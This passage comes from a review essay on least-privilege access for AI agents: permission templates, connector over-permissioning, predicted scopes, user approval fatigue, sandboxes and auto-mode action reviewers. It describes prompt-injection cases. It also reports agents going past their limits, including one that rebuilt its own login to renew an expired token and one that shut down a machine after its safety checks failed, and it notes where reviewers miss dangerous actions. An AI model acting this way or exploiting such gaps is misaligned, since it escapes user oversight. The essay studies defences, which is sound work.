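L3M's reader for untrusted bug reports, described earlier, can answer only "yes", "no" or "unclear". Eisenach and colleagues therefore calculate that a page can have at most log₂ 3, or about 1.6, bits of influence over the agent that acts, assuming that timing and failures reveal nothing more. If the task needs more than a one-word answer, the reader can return it in strict fields like those of Alhindi's invoice parser.

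Data passing from the acting agent to the reading agent needs a limit too. If the acting agent can write its own questions, it can put private data in them, and the reading agent may then send that data to a website. Fixing the questions before the acting agent opens any private file prevents this. Fixing only their length still allows a leak, but limits how much data each question can carry. ChainCaps does something similar within a single agent by withdrawing permission to send once the agent has read restricted data.

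The order of the work can also provide some separation. An agent could do all its web research first, then lose its network access before opening the private files. It couldn't send the files anywhere, but an injection from the research would still be in its prompt and could lead it to alter or delete them.

Using separate agents helps only if the receiving agent doesn't trust the messages too much. Anthropic warns that a system may trust a sub-agent's report more than a raw web page because the report comes from inside the system. An injection that gets into the report is then more likely to succeed than it was on the page.

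This design rules out tasks in which an unfamiliar page has to determine what the agent does with the user's authority. Suppose a supplier stops accepting emailed invoices and asks the user to submit them through a new website. Somebody has to read the site's instructions, work out which fields are required and fill them in while logged in as the user. A fixed menu can't contain the right answers, because nobody knew in advance what the site would require. The same problem arises when a coding agent has to install a program by following its documentation, or look up an error message that contains private code.

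A developer who knows the supplier's website can write a tool with fixed fields for it, so the agent needs no browser. The guarantees are therefore lost mainly on sites that nobody has prepared for, which are the main reason to give an agent a browser.

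## Who decides what the agent is given, and what does a narrow grant cost?

Somebody has to decide what access an agent gets, whether it works in a browser, a project folder or a bank account. The theorems about confinement and delegation don't help with this decision, because they show only that an agent stays within its grant. In the *DelegateGuard* tests, one unneeded web address in the root grant let most of the attacks succeed.

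A developer can write the grant in advance, the user can select the resources, a model can predict what the request will need, or the agent can ask for access as it works. Real systems often combine these methods.

### A developer writes the grant

Alhindi's invoice team gets its grants from a policy file that a developer writes before the system starts. Silverlock's *The Agent Access Model* describes a similar scheme from the network company Cloudflare, in which somebody defines a template once for each kind of task. For example, the template for a nightly accounting job might let an agent fetch a payment report, read two ledgers and post a summary to the finance channel. Each time the job starts, a trusted service grants only the access that the template allows and that whoever started the job also has. The credential expires when the task ends, and broader access requires a new task.

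Cloudflare's scheme uses logs to correct the templates. If many successful runs never use a permission, the system suggests removing it, and if failed runs repeatedly show the same refusal, it suggests adding one. A person decides whether to make the change, which applies only to later runs. Silverlock warns that both signals can mislead, because an attacker can repeat a forbidden request until it looks routine, and an unused permission may be meant for a rare emergency.

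Silverlock presents a reference architecture but no measurements from use. The scheme doesn't solve the problem of an agent that serves several people. If Alice may see revenue figures and Bob may not, an agent in their shared channel must either risk revealing the figures to Bob or limit itself to what both may see.

In practice, developers often grant too much. Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, examined the connectors that link ChatGPT and Claude to outside services. They compared the permissions each connector requested with the smallest set that would support the actions it offered. Six connectors requested more than they needed:

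| Connector | API methods allowed by the requested permissions | API methods allowed by the smallest sufficient set |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, Gmail | 50 | 32 |
| ChatGPT, Google Calendar | 12 | 5 |
| ChatGPT, Notion | 32 | 13 |
| ChatGPT, Dropbox | 44 | 25 |
| Claude, Google Drive | 45 | 27 |
| Claude, Notion | 32 | 29 |

ChatGPT's Gmail connector offered only read actions, but its permissions also covered changing and deleting emails. OpenAI may have corrected this since December 2025.

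### The user selects the resources

With a powerbox, the user grants a program access to a file by choosing it, so nobody has to write a policy. Claude Cowork does something similar with folders. The user selects a workspace folder, and Anthropic's virtual machine gives the agent's code access to only that folder and a settings folder on the user's computer. Cowork can mount a folder as read-only, read-write, or read-write without deletion.

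An injected instruction can't change a selection the user has already made. But selection works only for things the user can identify in advance. Someone who asks why a program keeps crashing doesn't know which files and servers matter. People also tend to select whole folders, so an agent that needs one invoice may receive them all. Anthropic's account of Cowork gives no figures on how much harm folder selection prevents or how often agents need something outside the folder.

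### A model predicts what the task needs

CapScope's ceiling comes from a model that sees the request and the project's file names before any agent reads the files. In *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents*, Noyan (2026) tested how accurately models predict the permissions a task needs. Noyan used 600 invented office tasks, each labelled with the correct permissions from a list of 15. Claude Haiku 4.5 saw six worked examples, while RoBERTa-large, a much smaller language model, was trained on 500 of the tasks. Both then predicted permissions for the remaining 100.

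| | Claude Haiku 4.5 | RoBERTa-large |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks given at least one unneeded permission | 42% | 23% |
| Tasks denied at least one needed permission | 11% | 21% |

Before the experiment, Noyan decided that a usable system should deny a needed permission in fewer than 10% of tasks and have an average precision (the share of granted permissions that the task needed) of at least 0.90. Neither model met both conditions at any of six settings. The most permissive setting lowered Haiku's denial rate to 10%, but also lowered its precision to 0.70. Frontier models also deny needed permissions and grant unneeded ones, according to a summary of the benchmark AuthBench in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents* (2026).

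Even imperfect predictions can remove a lot of unneeded access. Noyan weighted each permission by its risk and compared the grants with giving an agent all 15. Limits for each department removed 27.9% of the weighted total, and adding the predictions for each task raised this to 84.4%. That figure overstates the benefit, because it also counts needed permissions that the system wrongly withheld. No agent carried out the tasks, so the study didn't measure how many would have failed.

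The prediction is made before the agent reads files and web pages, which protects it from injections in them. This doesn't protect it from hostile text that the user has pasted into the request, and Noyan expects the predictor to grant whatever a poisoned description seems to need.

### The agent asks as it works

The agent can also start with almost no access and request more when it needs it, as the Model Context Protocol specification recommends. MiniScope automates the choice of what to request. It builds on OAuth, a standard that lets an application use someone's account without receiving the password. Services that support OAuth divide their functions into scopes, each permitting a set of API methods.

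From a service's public documentation, MiniScope records which methods each scope permits. It places one scope below another if its methods are a subset of the other's. The agent then submits a plan that lists the calls it intends to make, and MiniScope solves a small optimisation problem. Let x(v) be 1 if it selects scope v and 0 otherwise, and let cost(v) be the number of methods that v permits:

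minimise Σ cost(v) · x(v)

so that, for every call in the plan, at least one selected scope permits it.

Picking the narrowest scope for each call separately can give a worse result. Suppose a plan has to list events and list calendars, and a service offers three scopes:

```
P = {list events, search events}
Q = {list calendars, read settings}
R = {list events, list calendars, read time zones}
```

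The narrowest scope for the first call is P and the narrowest for the second is Q. Together, P and Q permit four methods, while R alone covers both calls and permits three. Such overlaps are common. In Google Calendar, an application can reach 24 of the 37 methods through more than one branch of the hierarchy.

MiniScope then asks the user whether to refuse the selected scopes or allow them once, for the session, or always. It checks every later call against the granted scopes and attaches the user's credentials itself, so the agent never has them.

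In one of Zhu and colleagues' examples, a user asks the agent to reply to an email that contains an instruction to delete it afterwards. The agent adds the deletion to its plan, so MiniScope requests full access to Gmail, which the user can refuse. The solver correctly found the smallest grant for the plan, but an attacker had influenced that plan. Security therefore depends on the user noticing the problem, and an attack that stays within the scopes already granted produces no request for the user to refuse.

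MiniScope added 1% to 6% to the agent's running time, not counting the time users take to answer. On tasks that involved several applications, the agent took 4.9 seconds on its own, 5.2 with MiniScope and 20.5 when GPT-5 chose the scopes. Commercial models chose the same minimum scopes as MiniScope for 70% to 83% of requests, and open models did so for 20% to 34%. A language model generated the requests, though the ten services were real. Zhu and colleagues didn't measure how many attacks MiniScope stops.

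The minimum grant also depends on how one weights permissions. Counting the methods a grant allows gives deleting an email the same weight as reading a time zone. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) points out that the MiniScope paper doesn't discuss whether its solution is unique. If a task can succeed with either the subject lines of all emails or the full text of one folder, neither grant contains the other. Someone has to judge which would be worse to leak, because an optimiser can't work that out from a list of methods.

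### The case against narrow grants

People use agents largely because they don't know in advance what a task will involve. A request to find out why a website is slow may lead to server logs, the database, the source code and a supplier's status page. A developer, user or model that has to choose the grant beforehand will either include all of these or stop the agent halfway. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) says researchers have no agreed way to evaluate such systems, and recommends that they report wrongful refusals and the burden on users as well as blocked attacks.

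Even a simple request can leave its limits unclear. In an example from *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026), a user asks four coding agents to tidy a folder of five files. Only two files are rubbish, but three of the agents also delete a backup of the user's credentials. Permission to delete files in that folder would have allowed this. A grant that named only the two rubbish files would have prevented it, but working out which files to delete was the task given to the agents.

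If the agent instead asks for access as it works, users soon stop reading the requests. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users approve 97% of permission prompts. Most prompts are probably harmless, so this figure alone doesn't show that users are careless. Anthropic therefore hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

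The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they may have cared less about damage. But that wouldn't easily explain why they became less careful as the session went on.

Users also turn narrow grants into wide ones. By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that lets Claude Code run some shell commands without asking. Five percent allowed every command, and another 43% allowed an interpreter such as Python, which is nearly as broad. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks turned off. These users began with frequent permission requests and ended up giving the agent something close to ambient authority.

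In Zhu and colleagues' simulation of three months of Gmail use, MiniScope users had to confirm between 18% and 60% of requests, depending on how cautious they were. That is far fewer prompts than asking about every method would produce, but probably still enough for confirming to become a habit.

Another objection is that somebody has to change the tools or put something between them and the system, because tool developers generally assumed that a program can open any file and contact any server. Most agent frameworks can't run on seL4 as they are, and Alhindi had to write the tools as small C programs.

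Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, show how much work this can take even when the policy already exists. Their prototype, from Brown University, enforces a different policy for each task on tools that the user doesn't trust. In their main example, a tool's description says that it writes a file, but its code also sends usage statistics over the network. The prototype handles it like this:

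1. An analyser inspects the tool's code and lists every way it can affect files or the network.
2. The user's side compares this list with the policy for the current task. If the policy forbids network access because the code is confidential, the user's side blocks the call.
3. The analyser can't know which file a future call will name. The tool's developer therefore wraps each file operation in a small sandbox, which checks the path against the policy when the call runs.
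4. The analyser confirms that the developer has wrapped every such operation and that no code alters the policy on the way.

Adam and colleagues tested three scenarios, each in an acceptable and a harmful version. The prototype decided correctly in all six cases, while the analysis alone did so in five and a fixed sandbox around the whole tool server did so in three. The sandbox wrongly blocked a change to a shell settings file and allowed two leaks. The results come from recorded sessions and scenarios that the designers chose, so they show that the method can work but not how often it would.

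The user doesn't have to know the tool, but its developer still has to rewrite it. The prototype also supports only tools written in Rust, and a remote tool would need special hardware to prove that the server runs the code the analyser inspected. The prototype takes the policy as given, so somebody still has to choose one.

Developers may also find capabilities hard to use. The evidence comes mainly from CHERI, a processor design in which each pointer is a capability that limits what memory a program can reach through it. In *Not quite a piece of CHERI-cake*, Alhindi and Hallett (2025) gave nine C programmers an 89-line program to adapt, which required changing the types of only five variables. All nine could explain what a CHERI capability is, and all fixed the first compiler warning, but three couldn't fix the second. Five were confident that the program would run despite the warnings,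 though it would have failed. A common pattern was to try changes at random, which Alhindi and Hallett call "floundering".

These programmers struggled with C pointers and unfamiliar warnings, which is quite different from deciding which folder an agent needs. The study is a better guide to how hard it is to build capability systems than to how hard it is to use a well-designed one. The difficulty of building them also varies. In *Biting the CHERI bullet* (2025), a study of defence teams, adapting one library took about 50 lines of changes. An earlier study that Alhindi and Hallett cite may be more relevant. It found that developers using Seccomp, a Linux mechanism for restricting programs, sometimes built sandboxes that didn't work.

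### Wrappers that leave the tools alone

Some tools need no rewriting. Microsoft's Azure SRE Agent, which diagnoses and repairs cloud services, runs standard programs such as `git` and Azure's command-line tool `az` unchanged. Mehta and Agarwal, two of its engineers, explain the design in *If you want a secure AI agent, start restricting its environment* (2026).

When the agent's GitHub token expired in an early test, the agent read the harness's source code, rebuilt the login procedure, prompted a researcher to complete it and saved the new tokens. Microsoft has since moved the tools into a virtual machine that holds no real credentials. When `git` requests a credential, it receives a handle that works for one call, one destination and one operation. A proxy outside the virtual machine checks the request and swaps the handle for a real credential. One proxy can therefore narrow the access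 of many existing programs, and the agent doesn't have to ask the user each time a handle expires.

The handles don't ensure that an action is right. In another incident, the agent was supposed to make five safety checks before it shut down a virtual machine. The logging service failed after the third, but the agent had permission to shut the machine down and did so anyway, because its memory included a similar case that had gone well. Mehta and Agarwal therefore still require a person to approve every change, while reads need no approval and the system blocks deletions. They are developing a separate check, based on the operation, its target and the evidence for it, so that low-risk changes can go ahead without a person's approval.

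Microsoft's documentation also describes a fallback for when the agent's own permissions are too narrow. The user is asked to approve the operation, and if they do, the agent performs it with the user's credentials. This lets the work continue, but it again relies on people reading what they approve. Microsoft gives no figures for how often the agent finishes its work or how many mistakes the design has prevented.

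### Fewer and better requests

The evidence for reducing the number of prompts is stronger. Claude Code's sandbox removed most of them in real use, though with a wide grant that lets the agent write anywhere in the workspace. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls the sandbox safe but "high-maintenance", because somebody has to configure each new capability.

Auto mode, the default for many Claude Code users since August 2026, replaces most permission prompts with a model that reviews each action. In the study with paid testers, it blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, far more than the testers themselves blocked. It still missed about one in nine, whereas an agent can never use a reference it wasn't given. The protection a reviewer offers is also harder to judge outside Anthropic's tests. *Explicit authorization scope improves LLM-based permission checking in coding agents*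 (2026) cites a stress test in which one product's auto mode approved most actions that went beyond the user's request. The paper found that such reviewers do better when somebody states what the agent may do, so a written grant can be useful even where a model makes the final decision.

People may also pay more attention to larger decisions, which would favor showing the user one grant at the start instead of fifty commands later. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans they see, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. But they may be rejecting plans because they dislike the proposed code, so the figures don't show that they would spot an excessive permission.

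### What agents lose in tests

In experiments, agents may have completed fewer tasks with narrow grants on seL4, while writing Scala for TACIT made little difference to completion. Neither experiment involved the hard part, which is choosing a grant without knowing the solution.

In Bouras and colleagues' test of CapScope, agents with a predicted ceiling on their permissions completed almost as many repairs as unrestricted ones. This is the most direct evidence that a model can choose a fairly narrow grant without ruining the work, but the projects were tiny and each request was for a specific repair. Short-lived grants were more disruptive in Santos-Grueiro's tests of PORTICO, where about a quarter of the tasks on real projects went unfinished. An agent that receives new handles automatically, as Microsoft's does, might avoid much of that loss, but Mehta and Agarwal report no comparison.

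Open-ended work needs a different test, in which nobody tailors the restrictions to the answer. *Permission Denied* (2026) proposes Boundary-Bench, which takes an existing coding benchmark and restricts the network, the filesystem or the agent's system privileges, each at one of three levels, without telling the agent. Comparing success and cost with an unrestricted run would show how much work each restriction prevents.
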